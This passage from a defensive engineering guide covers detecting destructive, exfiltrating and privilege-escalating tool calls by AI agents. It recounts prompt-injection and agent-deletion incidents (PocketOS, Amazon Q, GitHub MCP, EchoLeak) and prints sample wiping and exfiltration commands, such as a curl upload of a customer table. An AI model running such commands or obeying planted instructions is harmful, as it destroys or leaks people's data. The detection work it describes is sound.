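The list `destructive_operations` contains the operations in the table above, extended to cover every service the team uses. The word match catches unlisted operations by splitting each operation's name at capitals, hyphens and underscores and checking the pieces for a word that means deletion. It causes some false alarms, such as when an agent deletes a comment in a ticket system. Once a person has reviewed such an operation, they add it to `reviewed_operations` so that the word match ignores it.

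Ready-made rule sets can supply part of the list. Yang's AgentTrust ships with 170 default rules, including some for `kubectl`, Terraform, and the deployment tools Helm and ArgoCD. But any such set covers only the platforms its author thought of, so it may miss smaller providers where companies also keep production data.

### PocketOS: a deletion outside the big providers

On Friday 24 April 2026, Cursor, a coding agent running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes software that car rental firms use to run their bookings. According to founder Crane's account, *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, the agent was doing a routine task in the staging environment, a copy of the system for trying out changes. It ran into a credential mismatch and tried to fix this by deleting a volume (a virtual disk) at Railway,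 the company's hosting provider.

To do that, the agent needed an API token. It found one in a file that had nothing to do with the task, which is itself a form of privilege escalation. Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains, and says he didn't know that it could also delete volumes. The agent then used `curl` to send a single request to Railway's API, with this instruction in the body:

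```
mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...") }
```

The volume held production data, and the deletion took nine seconds. In Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab explains that the API carried out such requests immediately, with no way to undo them, although the same action in Railway's dashboard had a 48-hour grace period.

The two accounts differ on the backups. Crane posted his about 30 hours after the deletion, when the newest backup he could restore was three months old. He cited a warning in Railway's documentation that wiping a volume deletes its backups. Abdelwahab writes that the old API route also deleted the backup records, so the backups looked unavailable in the dashboard, but that Railway keeps separate off-site backups for disasters. Railway later recovered the database, as Tom's Hardware also reported in *Victim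 of AI agent that deleted company's entire database*. Articles that describe a permanent loss probably rely on Crane's first post.

Crane and Abdelwahab also disagree about how far Railway's tokens could be restricted. Crane says they can't be restricted by operation, environment or resource. Abdelwahab says Railway did offer tokens limited to a single workspace or project, but admits that the token creation page didn't make this option clear. On either account, a token created for managing domains could delete a production disk.

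A list of AWS verbs would have missed this call, since the agent used `curl` instead of `aws` and sent the request to Railway. Even a loose search for AWS's operation name, `DeleteVolume`, would have failed, because Railway puts the words in the opposite order. A rule that looks for the HTTP DELETE method would also have failed, because the agent used POST. Railway's API uses GraphQL, a query language in which the body of the request names the operation.

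DEL-CLOUD-01 catches the call if the parser can read the request body. The parser decodes the JSON in `curl`'s data option and finds the operation `volumeDelete`, which the word match splits into "volume" and "delete". The operation isn't on any list, so it gets grade 3. The single target adds 0 and the unknown environment adds 1, giving a score of 4, which requires a person's approval. Crane never requested a deletion, so he would probably have refused. If the parser can't read the body, the call should also require approval, as with any failed parse.

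Written instructions to the agent gave less protection. When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent quoted a rule against running destructive git commands unless asked. Read literally, that rule doesn't cover deleting a volume at a hosting provider, and neither does a list of AWS verbs. The explanation is weak evidence of why the agent acted, though, because the model wrote it afterwards.

Railway has since extended the 48-hour delay to deletions through the API. That lowers the starting grade of `volumeDelete` to 2 and the score to 3, so the verdict is still "ask". The delay doesn't cover data deleted from inside the volume. In a thread on Railway's forum, *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, a customer who had deleted tables with a database command asked for the same rescue as PocketOS. The customer was told that this was a very different situation,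 because Railway keeps a snapshot for deletions of the volume itself. Deleting tables inside a database therefore needs its own grade, usually 3.

### Amazon Q: planted instructions to delete everything

In July 2025, an attacker planted a prompt in Amazon's coding assistant Q, telling it to run ordinary AWS commands. According to AWS's bulletin AWS-2025-015, *Security Update for Amazon Q Developer Extension for Visual Studio Code* (2025), the extension's build configuration contained a GitHub token with too many permissions. The attacker used it to commit code to the extension's public repository, and an automatic release sent that code to users as version 1.84.0.

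The prompt told the agent to return the computer to a near-factory state, starting with the user's home directory. The agent was then supposed to find the AWS profiles stored on the machine and use them to list and delete cloud resources. TechRadar's *Hacker adds potentially catastrophic prompt to Amazon's AI coding service* quotes three of the suggested commands: `ec2 terminate-instances`, `s3 rm` and `iam delete-user`.

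A list of AWS operations covers all three commands if the detector parses them, which it must do because each has a `--profile` option after `aws`. Under DEL-CLOUD-01, terminating every machine in an unknown account scores 5, and the detector blocks it. Removing one file scores 3 or 4. Deleting one user scores only 2 if the team starts identities at grade 1, reasoning that a user holds no data. That is too lenient. Identities should start at grade 2 because recreating a user doesn't restore its keys, and any software that relies on them stops working.

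According to BeyondMachines' *Amazon Q Developer Extension for VS Code compromised*, the planted code started the agent with every tool approved in advance and without interactive prompts. Nobody could have answered an "ask" verdict, so the detector has to treat "ask" as "block" in sessions like that.

The attack did no reported damage. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2025-8217* (2025), an entry in the Spanish cybersecurity institute's vulnerability database, the planted code ran when the extension started, but a syntax error kept it from successfully calling the Q command-line program. The entry rates the severity as medium, at 5.1 out of 10. The commands probably wouldn't have worked, according to 404 Media's *Hacker Plants Computer 'Wiping' Commands in Amazon's AI Coding Agent*. The model apparently never received the prompt, so we can't tell from this case whether the agent would have obeyed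 it.

### Infrastructure-as-code changes that delete

Many harmful deletions come from commands that contain no deleting verb, so neither the list nor the word match finds them. The most common source is infrastructure as code, in which a team describes its cloud resources in files and a tool creates or changes the resources to match. One such tool, Terraform, compares the files with a "state file", its record of the resources it manages. Running `terraform apply` deletes any managed resource that is no longer in the files. It also deletes and recreates a resource if the provider can't make a change in place, so editing one setting of a database can replace it with an empty one.

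The remedy is to read Terraform's plan before allowing the change. HashiCorp's *JSON Output Format Overview* describes a machine-readable form of the plan, which a detector can use as follows:

1. The agent runs `terraform plan -out=plan.bin`, which saves the proposed changes to a file.
2. The detector converts the file with `terraform show -json plan.bin`.
3. It goes through the list `resource_changes` and picks out every entry whose actions include "delete". This also finds replacements, because Terraform records them as a deletion and a creation.
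4. It grades each deletion separately, takes the highest grade, and adds a point for scope if there are several.
5. If the verdict permits the change, the detector lets the agent apply that saved file, after checking that nobody has altered it.

A database that Terraform is about to replace appears in the plan like this:

```
"address": "aws_db_instance.main",
"change": { "actions": ["delete", "create"] },
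"action_reason": "replace_because_cannot_update"
```

The reason code helps the person who has to decide, but the verdict should depend only on the actions, because HashiCorp warns that the codes are display hints and may change. If the plan's `complete` field is false, at least one more round will probably be needed, and the detector has to read the next plan too. Running `terraform apply` without a saved plan file creates a new plan that the detector hasn't checked, so a person should be asked whether to allow it.

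A Terraform plan is misleading when the state file it depends on is wrong. *How I Dropped Our Production Database*, by Alexey Grigorev (alexeyondata), describes how this led to the loss of his online course platform in February 2026. He had moved to a new computer without copying the state file, so Terraform had no record of his existing infrastructure and began to create duplicates. He stopped it and told his agent, Claude Code, to delete only the duplicates. Meanwhile, he copied over an archive from the old computer. The agent unpacked the archive, which replaced the current state file with an older one, and then proposed `terraform destroy` as a cleaner method. The older file listed the production system, so Terraform deleted the database, the network and the servers.

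The automatic snapshots went too. AWS support found a copy that Grigorev couldn't see and restored it after 24 hours.

Requiring approval for every `terraform destroy` might not have helped. Grigorev saw the agent's proposal and let it continue because it seemed logical that Terraform should remove what Terraform had created. The approval prompt needs to list the resources that would be deleted. `terraform plan -destroy` would have listed the production database by name, giving him a chance to notice it.

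### Settings that delete later

A lifecycle policy on a storage bucket deletes files once they reach a certain age. MITRE gives the example of an attacker who uses the AWS call PutBucketLifecycle to delete every file in a bucket after one day. MITRE ATT&CK's *Detection of Lifecycle Policy Modifications for Triggered Deletion in IaaS Cloud Storage* (2025) recommends looking for very short expiry periods, with a threshold that each team can adjust.

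The threshold on its own misses some large deletions. AWS counts an object's age from its creation, so even a 365-day expiry policy removes almost everything in an archive of old records. A better test compares the expiry period with the ages of the objects in the bucket and counts how many the policy would delete within the next week. The detector can then grade the policy change as a deletion of those objects.

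Elastic's *AWS RDS Snapshot Deleted* (2024) matches calls that delete a database snapshot and calls to ModifyDBInstance that set the backup retention period to 0, which turns off automatic backups. Elastic's rule runs on logs after the event, but a detector can apply the same test to the arguments before the call runs. It should also compare the new retention period with the old one, because cutting it from 35 days to 1 removes most of the restore points but wouldn't match a test for zero.

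Scaling to zero stops a service without deleting its definition. `kubectl scale deployment shop --replicas=0` shuts down every copy of the `shop` service, and setting the size of an AWS machine group to zero terminates every machine in it. Judging the severity again requires looking up the current value, because a change from two copies to zero in a test cluster is routine, while a change from forty to zero in production takes a service offline. The Kubernetes change gets grade 1, because someone can scale the service up again. The AWS change may need grade 3, because terminated machines lose whatever was on their local disks.

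AWS's ScheduleKeyDeletion deletes an encryption key after a waiting period of 7 to 30 days, during which anyone with the right permission can cancel the deletion. After that, nobody can read data encrypted with the key, including backups. Grade 2 is correct only if somebody will notice before the period ends, so the detector should send an alert even when a person has approved the call. Disabling the key is a safer first step, since it has the same immediate effect and is easy to reverse. Yang's AgentTrust has 37 rules for suggesting safer commands like this alongside its verdict, and the suggestions never make the verdict more lenient.

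### Database migrations and the Supabase case

A migration changes the structure of a database, for example by adding a column. Migration tools often include commands that delete data freely because they are meant only for development. In *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database*, Madden (2026) names `prisma migrate reset`, which wipes a database, and `prisma db push`, which can delete data that doesn't fit the new structure. Madden leads engineering at Prisma, which makes these commands, and is promoting a new version without the reset command.

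In July 2026, a Prisma command that seems harmless emptied a live database hosted by Supabase. According to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1676* (2026), a developer had given Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 access to production so that it could repair the project's database schema. The agent ran `prisma migrate diff`, a command for comparing two schemas, and Prisma dropped all 22 tables. The developer later recovered or rebuilt most of the content. These details come largely from the developer's Reddit post, but Madden's explanation of the mechanism makes them plausible.

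Prisma determines the expected database schema by replaying all earlier migrations in a disposable "shadow database", which it wipes at the start of every run without a confirmation prompt. Hosting providers often don't let Prisma create this database automatically, so the developer has to supply an address. In this case, the agent put the production database's address in the shadow database field.

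DEL-CLOUD-01 doesn't match `migrate diff`, because the command isn't on the list and contains no word that means "delete". For each database tool, the detector needs a record of the fields that name a database the tool will wipe. When a call sets one of these fields, the detector works out the actual address and allows the call only if the address is on a list of disposable databases. A list of production databases would be less reliable, since somebody has to remember to add each new one.

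A detector also needs a rule for the override flags. As Madden points out, when a warning stops one of these tools, the error message often names the flag that bypasses the warning, and an agent trying to complete the command may add that flag. A call with `--accept-data-loss` or `--force-reset` should at least trigger a request for confirmation. Prisma's new version also labels each planned operation as additive, widening, data or destructive. A detector can read these labels as it reads Terraform's plan, but it relies on the tool to apply them correctly.

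### When the identifier doesn't show the environment

The PocketOS volume's identifier began with `3d2c42fb`, and nothing in it showed whether the volume was in production. Most cloud identifiers don't show this either, so a detector that searches for "prod" in a call will miss production resources with such identifiers. It will also raise false alarms about a test machine named `product-search`.

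The usual remedy is to look up the resource before deciding. Cloud providers let teams attach tags such as `environment: production` to resources. When a call matches the deletion rule, the detector fetches the target's tags from the provider, using its own read-only credentials. Only a small share of calls match, so the extra request adds little time overall. The detector should treat a resource with no environment tag as production. If the agent has permission to edit tags, it could relabel a resource by mistake or because of injected text, so the detector should also check when the tag last changed. Keeping test and production in separate accounts avoids this problem.

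Labels in a project's own files are less trustworthy. AI Incident Database's *Production database servers* records a case from July 2026 in which the software engineer Bruno Lemos asked OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol to generate sample data for local testing. The agent ran the project's tests and then a clean-up step that emptied the `users` table and every table that refers to it. The project's setting for the test database contained the address of the live one. A detector that relied on the word "test" in the setting's name would have allowed the command. The detector has to compare the address with the list of disposable databases before the tests start, because the command that starts them may contain no reference to deletion.

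### Routine clean-up that looks the same

Teams delete cloud resources every day to save money. According to Elastic's notes on its snapshot rule, many environments routinely delete old snapshots, and the rule excludes deletions by AWS's backup service. Coding agents add to these routine deletions when they clean up after their tests.

The most useful distinction is whether the agent created the resource. When a provider creates a resource, it returns an identifier, which the detector can save in the session's record. If the agent deletes that resource later in the same session, the detector can subtract two points from the score. It subtracts the same amount for a test account, but never applies both reductions. In Grigorev's case, this would have separated the duplicates, which the agent had created, from the production database, which it had not. The detector must take the identifiers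 from the provider's responses, because the agent's own account of what it created may be wrong.

Older resources need a different test, since no session record covers them. For snapshots, the detector can check what would remain, because deleting the oldest of thirty is ordinary maintenance but deleting the last one leaves the database without a restore point. The detector can also compare the number of deletions with the usual number. If a weekly clean-up normally removes about ten disks and the agent proposes to remove four hundred, a person should look at the list first. A clean-up that follows a fixed schedule is better run as an ordinary script under its own identity. The agent then has no reason to delete old resources, so the detector can be strict about any attempt by the agent to do so.

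## Detecting transfers of data to outside destinations

A deletion rule can start from a list of operations, but no particular operation identifies data exfiltration. Agents routinely upload files, send web requests, write emails, push code and copy files between buckets, and any of these calls can also send a customer table outside the company. Blocking these operations would also block legitimate work, so an exfiltration rule has to check the data and the destination together.

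### Listing the channels

A channel is any way a tool call can give data to outsiders. For each channel, the rule's author records which parts of a call contain the destination and the data.

| Channel | Destination | Data |
|---|---|---|
| Web request | The host, and the account that the path or key selects | Body, headers and the address itself |
| Copy to cloud storage | The bucket and the account that owns it | The source file or bucket |
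| Code push | The repository behind the remote's name | Every commit that the repository doesn't have yet |
| Email or chat message | All recipients, including blind copies | Subject, text and attachments |
| Ticket, comment or pull request | The project, and everyone who can read it | Every text field |
| MCP tool | The server's operator, and any service behind it | Every argument |
| Sharing setting | The account that gains access | The resource that the call opens |

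A tool's purpose is a poor guide to whether it belongs on this list. *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026), by the security vendor CrowdStrike, describes a tool that adds two numbers but also accepts a free-text "sidenote". A hidden instruction in the tool's description tells the agent to put the user's private SSH key in that field, so the MCP server receives the key and the tool still returns the correct sum. In another example, a tool description makes the agent add an outsider to the blind-copy field of an ordinary email. Both examples are illustrations, not incidents, but someone compiling the list in a hurry could easily leave out both fields. CrowdStrike recommends defining the allowed values of every parameter and checking network destinations before a tool runs. For the addition tool, the detector could reject any call that contains text.

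Some tool calls show neither the destination nor the data. For example, `git push origin main` sends commits to whatever address the project's settings store under the name `origin`. The detector has to look up that address just before the push, because the agent may have changed it with an earlier command. It also has to examine each new commit separately. If one commit adds a password and the next removes it, the final files no longer contain it, but the push still sends it as part of the commit history.

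### Writing the list of trusted destinations

Each entry in the list needs a clearance, the highest class of data that the destination may receive. Four classes are enough for most teams:

- Class 0: published material, such as open-source code and public documentation.
- Class 1: ordinary internal material, including anything nobody has marked.
- Class 2: customer records, personal data and trade secrets.
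- Class 3: credentials.

```
trusted_destinations:
  - bucket: acme-builds
    owner_account: "444455556666"
    clearance: 1
  - bucket: acme-warehouse
    owner_account: "444455556666"
    clearance: 2
  - repository: github.com/acme/shop       # private
    clearance: 1
  - repository: github.com/acme/website    # public
    clearance: 0
```

A destination's clearance depends on who can read it, regardless of who owns it. The company owns its public website repository, but anyone can read what an agent posts there, so the repository gets the same clearance as an unknown host.

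Allowlist entries should name an account, bucket or repository rather than a domain, because every AWS customer stores files under Amazon's domains and every GitHub user publishes under github.com. Even a bucket's name may not show who owns it. If the company deletes `acme-builds`, a stranger may be able to create a new bucket with that name, and the old entry would then allow uploads to it. AWS lets a caller specify which account should own the bucket and refuses the request if another account does, so the detector can require uploads to specify the expected owner.

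Claude Code has an "auto mode", in which a language model approves or blocks tool calls in place of the user. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the model treats only the current code repository as trusted by default, and users can add domains, buckets, source-control organisations and internal services. This default is narrow enough for private projects, but if the repository is public, a detector should still check what the agent puts in it. The same applies when a user adds a whole source-control organisation, since many organisations have both public and private repositories.

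Detecting transfers to a real attacker's domain requires a list of trusted destinations rather than a list of known bad hosts, because the domain may be a day old and is rarely easy to recognise. Yang reports 98% accuracy on 50 exfiltration scenarios, but four of the rules in that test matched invented attacker domains such as `evil.com`. Yang leaves these four out of the production rules, and without them, accuracy across all 300 scenarios drops from 97% to 95%.

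Users often name a new destination, for example by asking the agent to email a summary to a client. The detector can give that address clearance 1 for the session, so that the user doesn't have to confirm a request they just made. It must take the address only from the user's messages, because a web page or document that the agent reads may contain an attacker's address. Sending customer records still requires a permanent entry for the destination that somebody has reviewed.

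### Marking sensitive data

A detector can recognise sensitive data in four ways, and should use the highest class that any of them gives:

- **Path.** Yang's rules cover the credential files `.aws/credentials`, `.kube/config` and `~/.netrc`, which belong in class 3. A team adds its own folders, such as the one where its database exports go.
- **Table.** The team records which database tables and columns hold personal data. The detector parses the query and looks up each one. If it can't tell which columns a query returns, it uses the highest class in the database.
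- **Label.** Many companies already tag buckets or put sensitivity labels on documents. The detector should fetch these with its own credentials, and treat a recent downgrade as suspicious.
- **Pattern.** Many access keys have a fixed prefix and length, and payment card numbers contain a check digit. The detector can search the outgoing text for both.

Each method misses data that another may catch. A path check may miss a renamed copy of a file, but the card numbers inside still match a pattern. Pattern matching misses ordinary passwords because they have no fixed form, though the path of the file that holds them may be on the list. Counting matches also helps with personal data, since one email address in a message is normal and five hundred are probably a customer list.

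Every authenticated request contains a credential, so the detector needs an exception to class 3 for keys in the headers of requests to their own services. It can store a fingerprint of each company key with the hosts where the key belongs, and treat the key as class 3 anywhere else. Internal destinations need this check too, because agents can also leak credentials inside the company. Anthropic's incident log describes an agent that uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal compute cluster.

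### The decision table

The detector subtracts the destination's clearance from the data's class:

gap = class − clearance

| Data | Clearance 0: unlisted or public | Clearance 1 | Clearance 2 | Clearance 3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Class 0, published | Allow | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| Class 1, internal | Ask | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| Class 2, customer records | Block | Ask | Allow | Allow |
| Class 3, credentials | Block | Block | Ask | Allow |

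Only a destination such as the company's secrets manager should have clearance 3. The table has no "warn", because nobody can recall the data after a warning. As a rule, it looks like this:

```
id: EXF-SEND-01
name: Data sent to a destination not cleared for it
action_types: [shell_command, api_call, network_request,
               code_execution]
match:
  channel_in: channels
severity: high
data_class: highest class of any source, otherwise 1
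clearance: lowest clearance of any destination
verdict:
  gap of 0 or less: allow
  gap of 1: ask
  gap of 2 or more: block
exemptions: none
tags: [T1537, AML.T0086]
```

An email to nine colleagues and one stranger is therefore checked against the stranger's clearance. If the detector can't determine what data a call sends, it treats the data as class 1, which can go to a company bucket without approval but needs approval to go anywhere else.

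Suppose an agent proposes three uploads:

```
aws s3 cp build/app.zip s3://acme-builds/
curl -F file=@exports/customers.csv https://files.example.net/in
aws s3 cp exports/customers.csv s3://northwind-drop/
```

| Call | Class | Clearance | Gap | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Build file to the company's bucket | 1 | 1 | 0 | Allow |
| Customer table to an unknown host | 2 | 0 | 2 | Block |
| Customer table to another party's bucket on AWS | 2 | 0 | 2 | Block |

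The two `aws` commands use the same program and the same provider's domain, so a rule that trusted Amazon's domain would allow both, but the list of buckets distinguishes them. If Northwind is a partner with a contract to receive the table, the company adds Northwind's bucket and account number to the list with clearance 2, and the same rule then allows the call.

Anthropic describes a milder case in which an agent tried to share a script for debugging by publishing it as a Gist, a snippet on GitHub. Claude Code's auto mode blocks this because the user may consider the script confidential. The gap in the table is 1, so the detector would ask the user. Asking seems better than blocking when the user is there to answer, since only they know whether the script is confidential.

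### Sharing data in place

An agent can give outsiders access to data without sending it to them, by changing a setting so that they can fetch it themselves.

| Change | AWS operation | Where the call names the outsider |
|---|---|---|
| Open a bucket | PutBucketPolicy, PutBucketAcl | The principals or grantees; `*` in a policy means everyone |
| Share a disk snapshot | ModifySnapshotAttribute | An account number, or the group `all` |
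| Share a database snapshot | ModifyDBSnapshotAttribute | An account number, or `all` |
| Copy new files continuously | PutBucketReplication | The destination bucket and its account |
| Create a temporary link | None, because the program signs the link locally | Nowhere; anyone with the link can use it |

When an agent gives an outside account access to data in cloud storage, egress monitoring, which watches the traffic leaving the agent's environment, can't detect the transfer by volume or destination. The agent sends only a short request to the cloud provider's API, which it contacts routinely. The data then moves from the provider's storage to the outsider's machine, or between two accounts inside the provider's network, without passing through the agent's environment. Even if a proxy decrypts the request, a content filter has no customer data to match, because the request contains only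 a setting and an account number.

Once a single call has created a replication rule, AWS copies every new file in the bucket to the destination for as long as the rule exists. The later calls that add files to the bucket are ordinary internal uploads, so the detector's only good chance to stop the transfer is the call that creates the rule.

EXF-SEND-01 also works for sharing if the detector treats the resource as the data and the account that gains access as the destination. Sharing a snapshot of the customer database with an unlisted account gives 2 − 0 = 2, so the detector blocks it. Making a bucket of website images public gives 0 − 0 = 0, so the detector allows it. An unlabelled snapshot of a production database should start at class 2, because it contains every table.

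Bucket policies take more work because they can hold many statements, and PutBucketPolicy replaces the whole policy. The detector can handle them in four steps:

1. It fetches the current policy and compares it with the proposed one.
2. It picks out every new or altered statement that allows access, and every statement denying access that the new policy drops.
3. It looks up the clearance of each account that gains access, using 0 for everyone.
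4. It compares the lowest clearance with the bucket's class.

Policy conditions complicate the third step. A policy may name everyone but limit access to the company's own organisation, which makes it private in effect. If the detector can't evaluate a condition, it should ask a person. AWS also has a block on public access that overrides public policies. The detector should ask about any call that removes this block, even before anyone makes the bucket public. The block doesn't prevent sharing with one named outside account, so the detector has to check for that separately.

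The detector needs a rule for commands that create temporary links. `aws s3 presign` uses the agent's credentials to create a web address that lets anyone who has it download one file until the link expires. The command sends no request to AWS, so AWS logs don't record the link's creation. The detector can compare the file's class with clearance 0 when the agent creates the link, or it can give the link the same class as the file and check that class against each destination the agent sends the link to.

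### Private repositories leaked through GitHub's own tools

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack in which every tool was genuine and the destination belonged to the victim. The company's researchers set up a demonstration account with one public repository and several private ones, and connected Anthropic's Claude Desktop to it through GitHub's MCP server. They then posted an issue containing instructions for an agent in the public repository, as any stranger could. When the user asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues, the agent followed the instructions, read the private repositories and described them in a public pull request. The description included the names of private projects, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America.

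Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow". The researchers argue that the flaw isn't in GitHub's code and that GitHub can't fix it through server changes alone. They propose limiting an agent to one repository per session, which would have prevented this leak but would also stop an agent from copying a fix between two private projects. A narrower rule would only block an agent from writing to a public repository after it has read a private one. Invariant Labs sells software that enforces such rules, so it has an interest in recommending them, but its reasoning is sound regardless.

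GitHub added two defences later that year. In August, GitHub (2025) announced that its hosted MCP server scans the inputs of tool calls to public repositories for credentials and blocks any call that contains one, although most users can override the block. GitHub acknowledged that this doesn't stop leaks of other data, so it wouldn't catch a salary or a travel plan. In December, GitHub (2025) introduced a "Lockdown mode" which, according to GitHub, hides issues and comments in public repositories unless their author has permission to push code. This would have hidden the planted issue from the agent, but it would also hide bug reports from ordinary users, which maintainers often want an agent to sort.

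The same kind of leak appeared in July 2026 in another product, GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs agents automatically in response to events in a repository. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) lists isolation, constrained outputs and logging among the product's protections. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reports that researchers at the security firm Noma Labs posted an issue that looked like a request from a sales executive, and the agent copied a private repository's README file into a public comment.

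Limiting the kinds of output an agent can produce doesn't help much when the leak is an ordinary comment. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) treats the workflow's configuration as part of the problem, and Noma proposed a documentation note about sharing keys between repositories. The Next Web wrote that GitHub had neither added the note nor answered questions from The Register, a technology news site, but Kiteworks' *GitHub's AI Agent Leaked Private Code With One Word*, a vendor's newsletter, says GitHub did update its documentation after the disclosure.

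### Microsoft 365 Copilot: a leak without an outgoing tool call

In June 2026, the security company Varonis disclosed a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot's search of company emails and files. According to Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), a victim only had to click a link to a genuine Microsoft address. Copilot treated text in the link as an instruction, searched the victim's mailbox and wrote an answer containing an image whose address included the title of an email. The victim's browser loaded the image while the answer was still appearing, before Microsoft's clean-up step could disable it.

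Microsoft's page accepted images only from certain domains, but these included Bing, which offered a function that fetches an image from any address it receives. When Bing fetched the image, it passed the email's title to the researchers' server, although the browser had contacted only Microsoft.

According to The Hacker News (2026), Microsoft rated the flaw critical but gave it a severity score of 6.5 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Varonis demonstrated the attack but didn't report that anyone had used it.

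Rules on tool calls would probably have missed this leak, because the browser sent the data and the agent's only visible action was searching the user's own mailbox, which is what the product is for. The remedy belongs in the software that displays answers. Varonis recommends removing dangerous content before the browser shows it, and treating any trusted domain that fetches URLs for its users as a possible route for leaking data. A stricter remedy is to load no images at all, which GitHub chose in 2025 after a similar flaw in its Copilot Chat, according to OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025).

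Attackers could exploit EchoLeak, an earlier flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, without the user clicking anything. Reddy and Gujral's *EchoLeak* describes how a single email could evade Microsoft's filter for prompt injection and make the assistant send out company data. Microsoft said that nobody had exploited the flaw, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*.

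In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, Willison (2025) attributes such leaks to a "lethal trifecta" of access to private data, exposure to malicious text, and a way to send data out. The GitHub and Microsoft attacks all fit this description. Removing any one of the three stops the attack, which suggests a useful design test. But an agent can leak data by mistake without any malicious text, so a team that removes only exposure to such text still needs rules on sending data out.

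### Where the rules break

**Encoded and paraphrased content.** The detector can undo common encodings before matching and open archives up to a fixed depth and size, but it can't read encrypted files without the key. Classifying data by its source works better, because a customer table stays in class 2 after compression. If the source is unknown and the content is unreadable, the detector should require approval before the data goes to an unlisted destination.

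A language model can recognise some disguised data that pattern matching misses, although Anthropic's classifier still let through 5.7% of 1,000 generated exfiltration attempts. Paraphrased data is harder to detect than encoded data. For example, an agent can write that the company's largest client plans to leave in March, a sentence that contains no name, number or key. Pattern matching on the content won't catch this reliably, so the detector has to judge the call by its destination and by what the agent has read.

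**Secrets in an address or a name lookup.** Fetching a web page also sends data out, because the host receives the full address, which can contain a key or a sentence. The detector should treat every fetch as a transfer, decode the address and search it for sensitive patterns. It can also ask for approval before the agent fetches an address it composed itself on an unlisted host, while allowing addresses that came unchanged from the user or a search engine. Some information can still leak, because a site's owner can learn something from which of several permitted pages the agent requests.

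A name lookup can send data out before the machine connects to a host. The machine first looks up the host's numeric address in the domain name system, and that query can reach a server run by the domain's owner. Any data in the host name has then leaked, even if the connection fails. A detector can check host names in the tool call before the lookup happens, but it can't check names that a script builds while running. Blocking those lookups requires a name server that resolves only approved domains.

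Attackers can use trusted code hosts, file-sharing services and online forms as easily as the company can. When the address identifies the account or repository, the company can list that as trusted instead of the whole site. On some services, however, the API key in the request determines which account receives the data, so an upload made with an outsider's key goes to the outsider's account. The detector should accept only keys whose fingerprints the company has registered, and give any other key clearance 0. For services that fetch addresses on request, as Bing did, the detector should also check the address they are asked to fetch.

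Once a customer's record is in an agent's context, the agent can repeat it in any text field of any later call. The repeated text no longer has the path, table name or label that would show where it came from. Pattern matching may find a card number in it, but won't find a salary in a pull request. A rule that examines one call at a time can't connect that salary to the record the agent read earlier.

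The remedy is to record what the agent has read across calls. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, builds on decentralised information flow control, a security model that tracks how secret and how trustworthy each piece of data is as it moves through a system. The simplest version treats every outgoing call as containing the most sensitive class of data the session has read so far. This is safe but imprecise, because after reading one customer record the agent can't send even a harmless web search to an unlisted host. Running work on customer data in a separate session, with no outside channels, avoids most of these false alarms.

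## Detecting changes to permissions in cloud accounts and Kubernetes

An identity can gain permissions without any change to its own policies, so a detector of privilege escalation has to count everything that the identity can make happen. Let P(j) be the set of operation and resource pairs that identity j's policies allow, such as "stop" and "machine i-0a1". Let C(i) be the identities that i controls: i itself, any identity whose credentials i holds, and any identity under which i's own code runs. The effective permissions of i are

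E(i) = all pairs in P(j), for every j in C(i)

and a call is an escalation if E(i) afterwards contains a pair that it lacked before. This can happen in three ways:

- A direct grant changes the account's identities or policies, for example by attaching a policy to i or creating a key for another user.
- An indirect gain leaves every policy alone, but i's code starts to run under a stronger role.
- With a found credential, nothing in the account changes. The agent comes across a stronger key or token and uses it.

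### Direct grants on AWS, Google Cloud and Azure

A rule for direct grants starts from a list of operations.

| What changes | AWS | Google Cloud | Azure |
|---|---|---|---|
| What an identity may do | AttachUserPolicy, AttachRolePolicy, PutUserPolicy, PutRolePolicy, AddUserToGroup | `gcloud projects add-iam-policy-binding` | `az role assignment create` |
| The contents of a policy or role already in use | CreatePolicyVersion, SetDefaultPolicyVersion | `gcloud iam roles update` | `az role definition update` |
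| Who may act as an identity | UpdateAssumeRolePolicy | `gcloud iam service-accounts add-iam-policy-binding` | `az identity federated-credential create` |
| The credentials of another identity | CreateAccessKey, CreateLoginProfile, UpdateLoginProfile | `gcloud iam service-accounts keys create` | `az ad sp credential reset` |

Some of these calls don't list any permissions. SetDefaultPolicyVersion switches a policy to a version that AWS already stores, so the call contains only the policy's name and a version number. The detector has to fetch that version to determine what it allows. AddUserToGroup likewise contains only the names of a user and a group.

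CreateAccessKey is an escalation only if the key belongs to another user, since replacing one's own key adds no permissions. The rule therefore has to compare the caller with the key's owner. If the call names no user, AWS creates the key for the caller.

The detector also has to check where a grant applies. On Azure, the Contributor role on one storage account lets an identity manage that account, while the same role on a subscription lets it manage nearly every resource in the subscription. The commands for these two grants differ only in the `--scope` option.

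Removing a policy can also widen permissions. A deny statement in an AWS policy overrides any allow statement, so detaching a policy that contains one may give an identity more access. Calls that detach or delete policies therefore belong on the list, as do calls that remove a permissions boundary, which limits the permissions that an identity's policies can grant.

### Role bindings and special verbs in Kubernetes

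Kubernetes has a safeguard that AWS lacks. According to Kubernetes' *Using RBAC Authorization*, users can create a role, change it or bind it to someone only if they already hold every permission in it. An agent with ordinary rights therefore can't give itself new permissions by editing roles.

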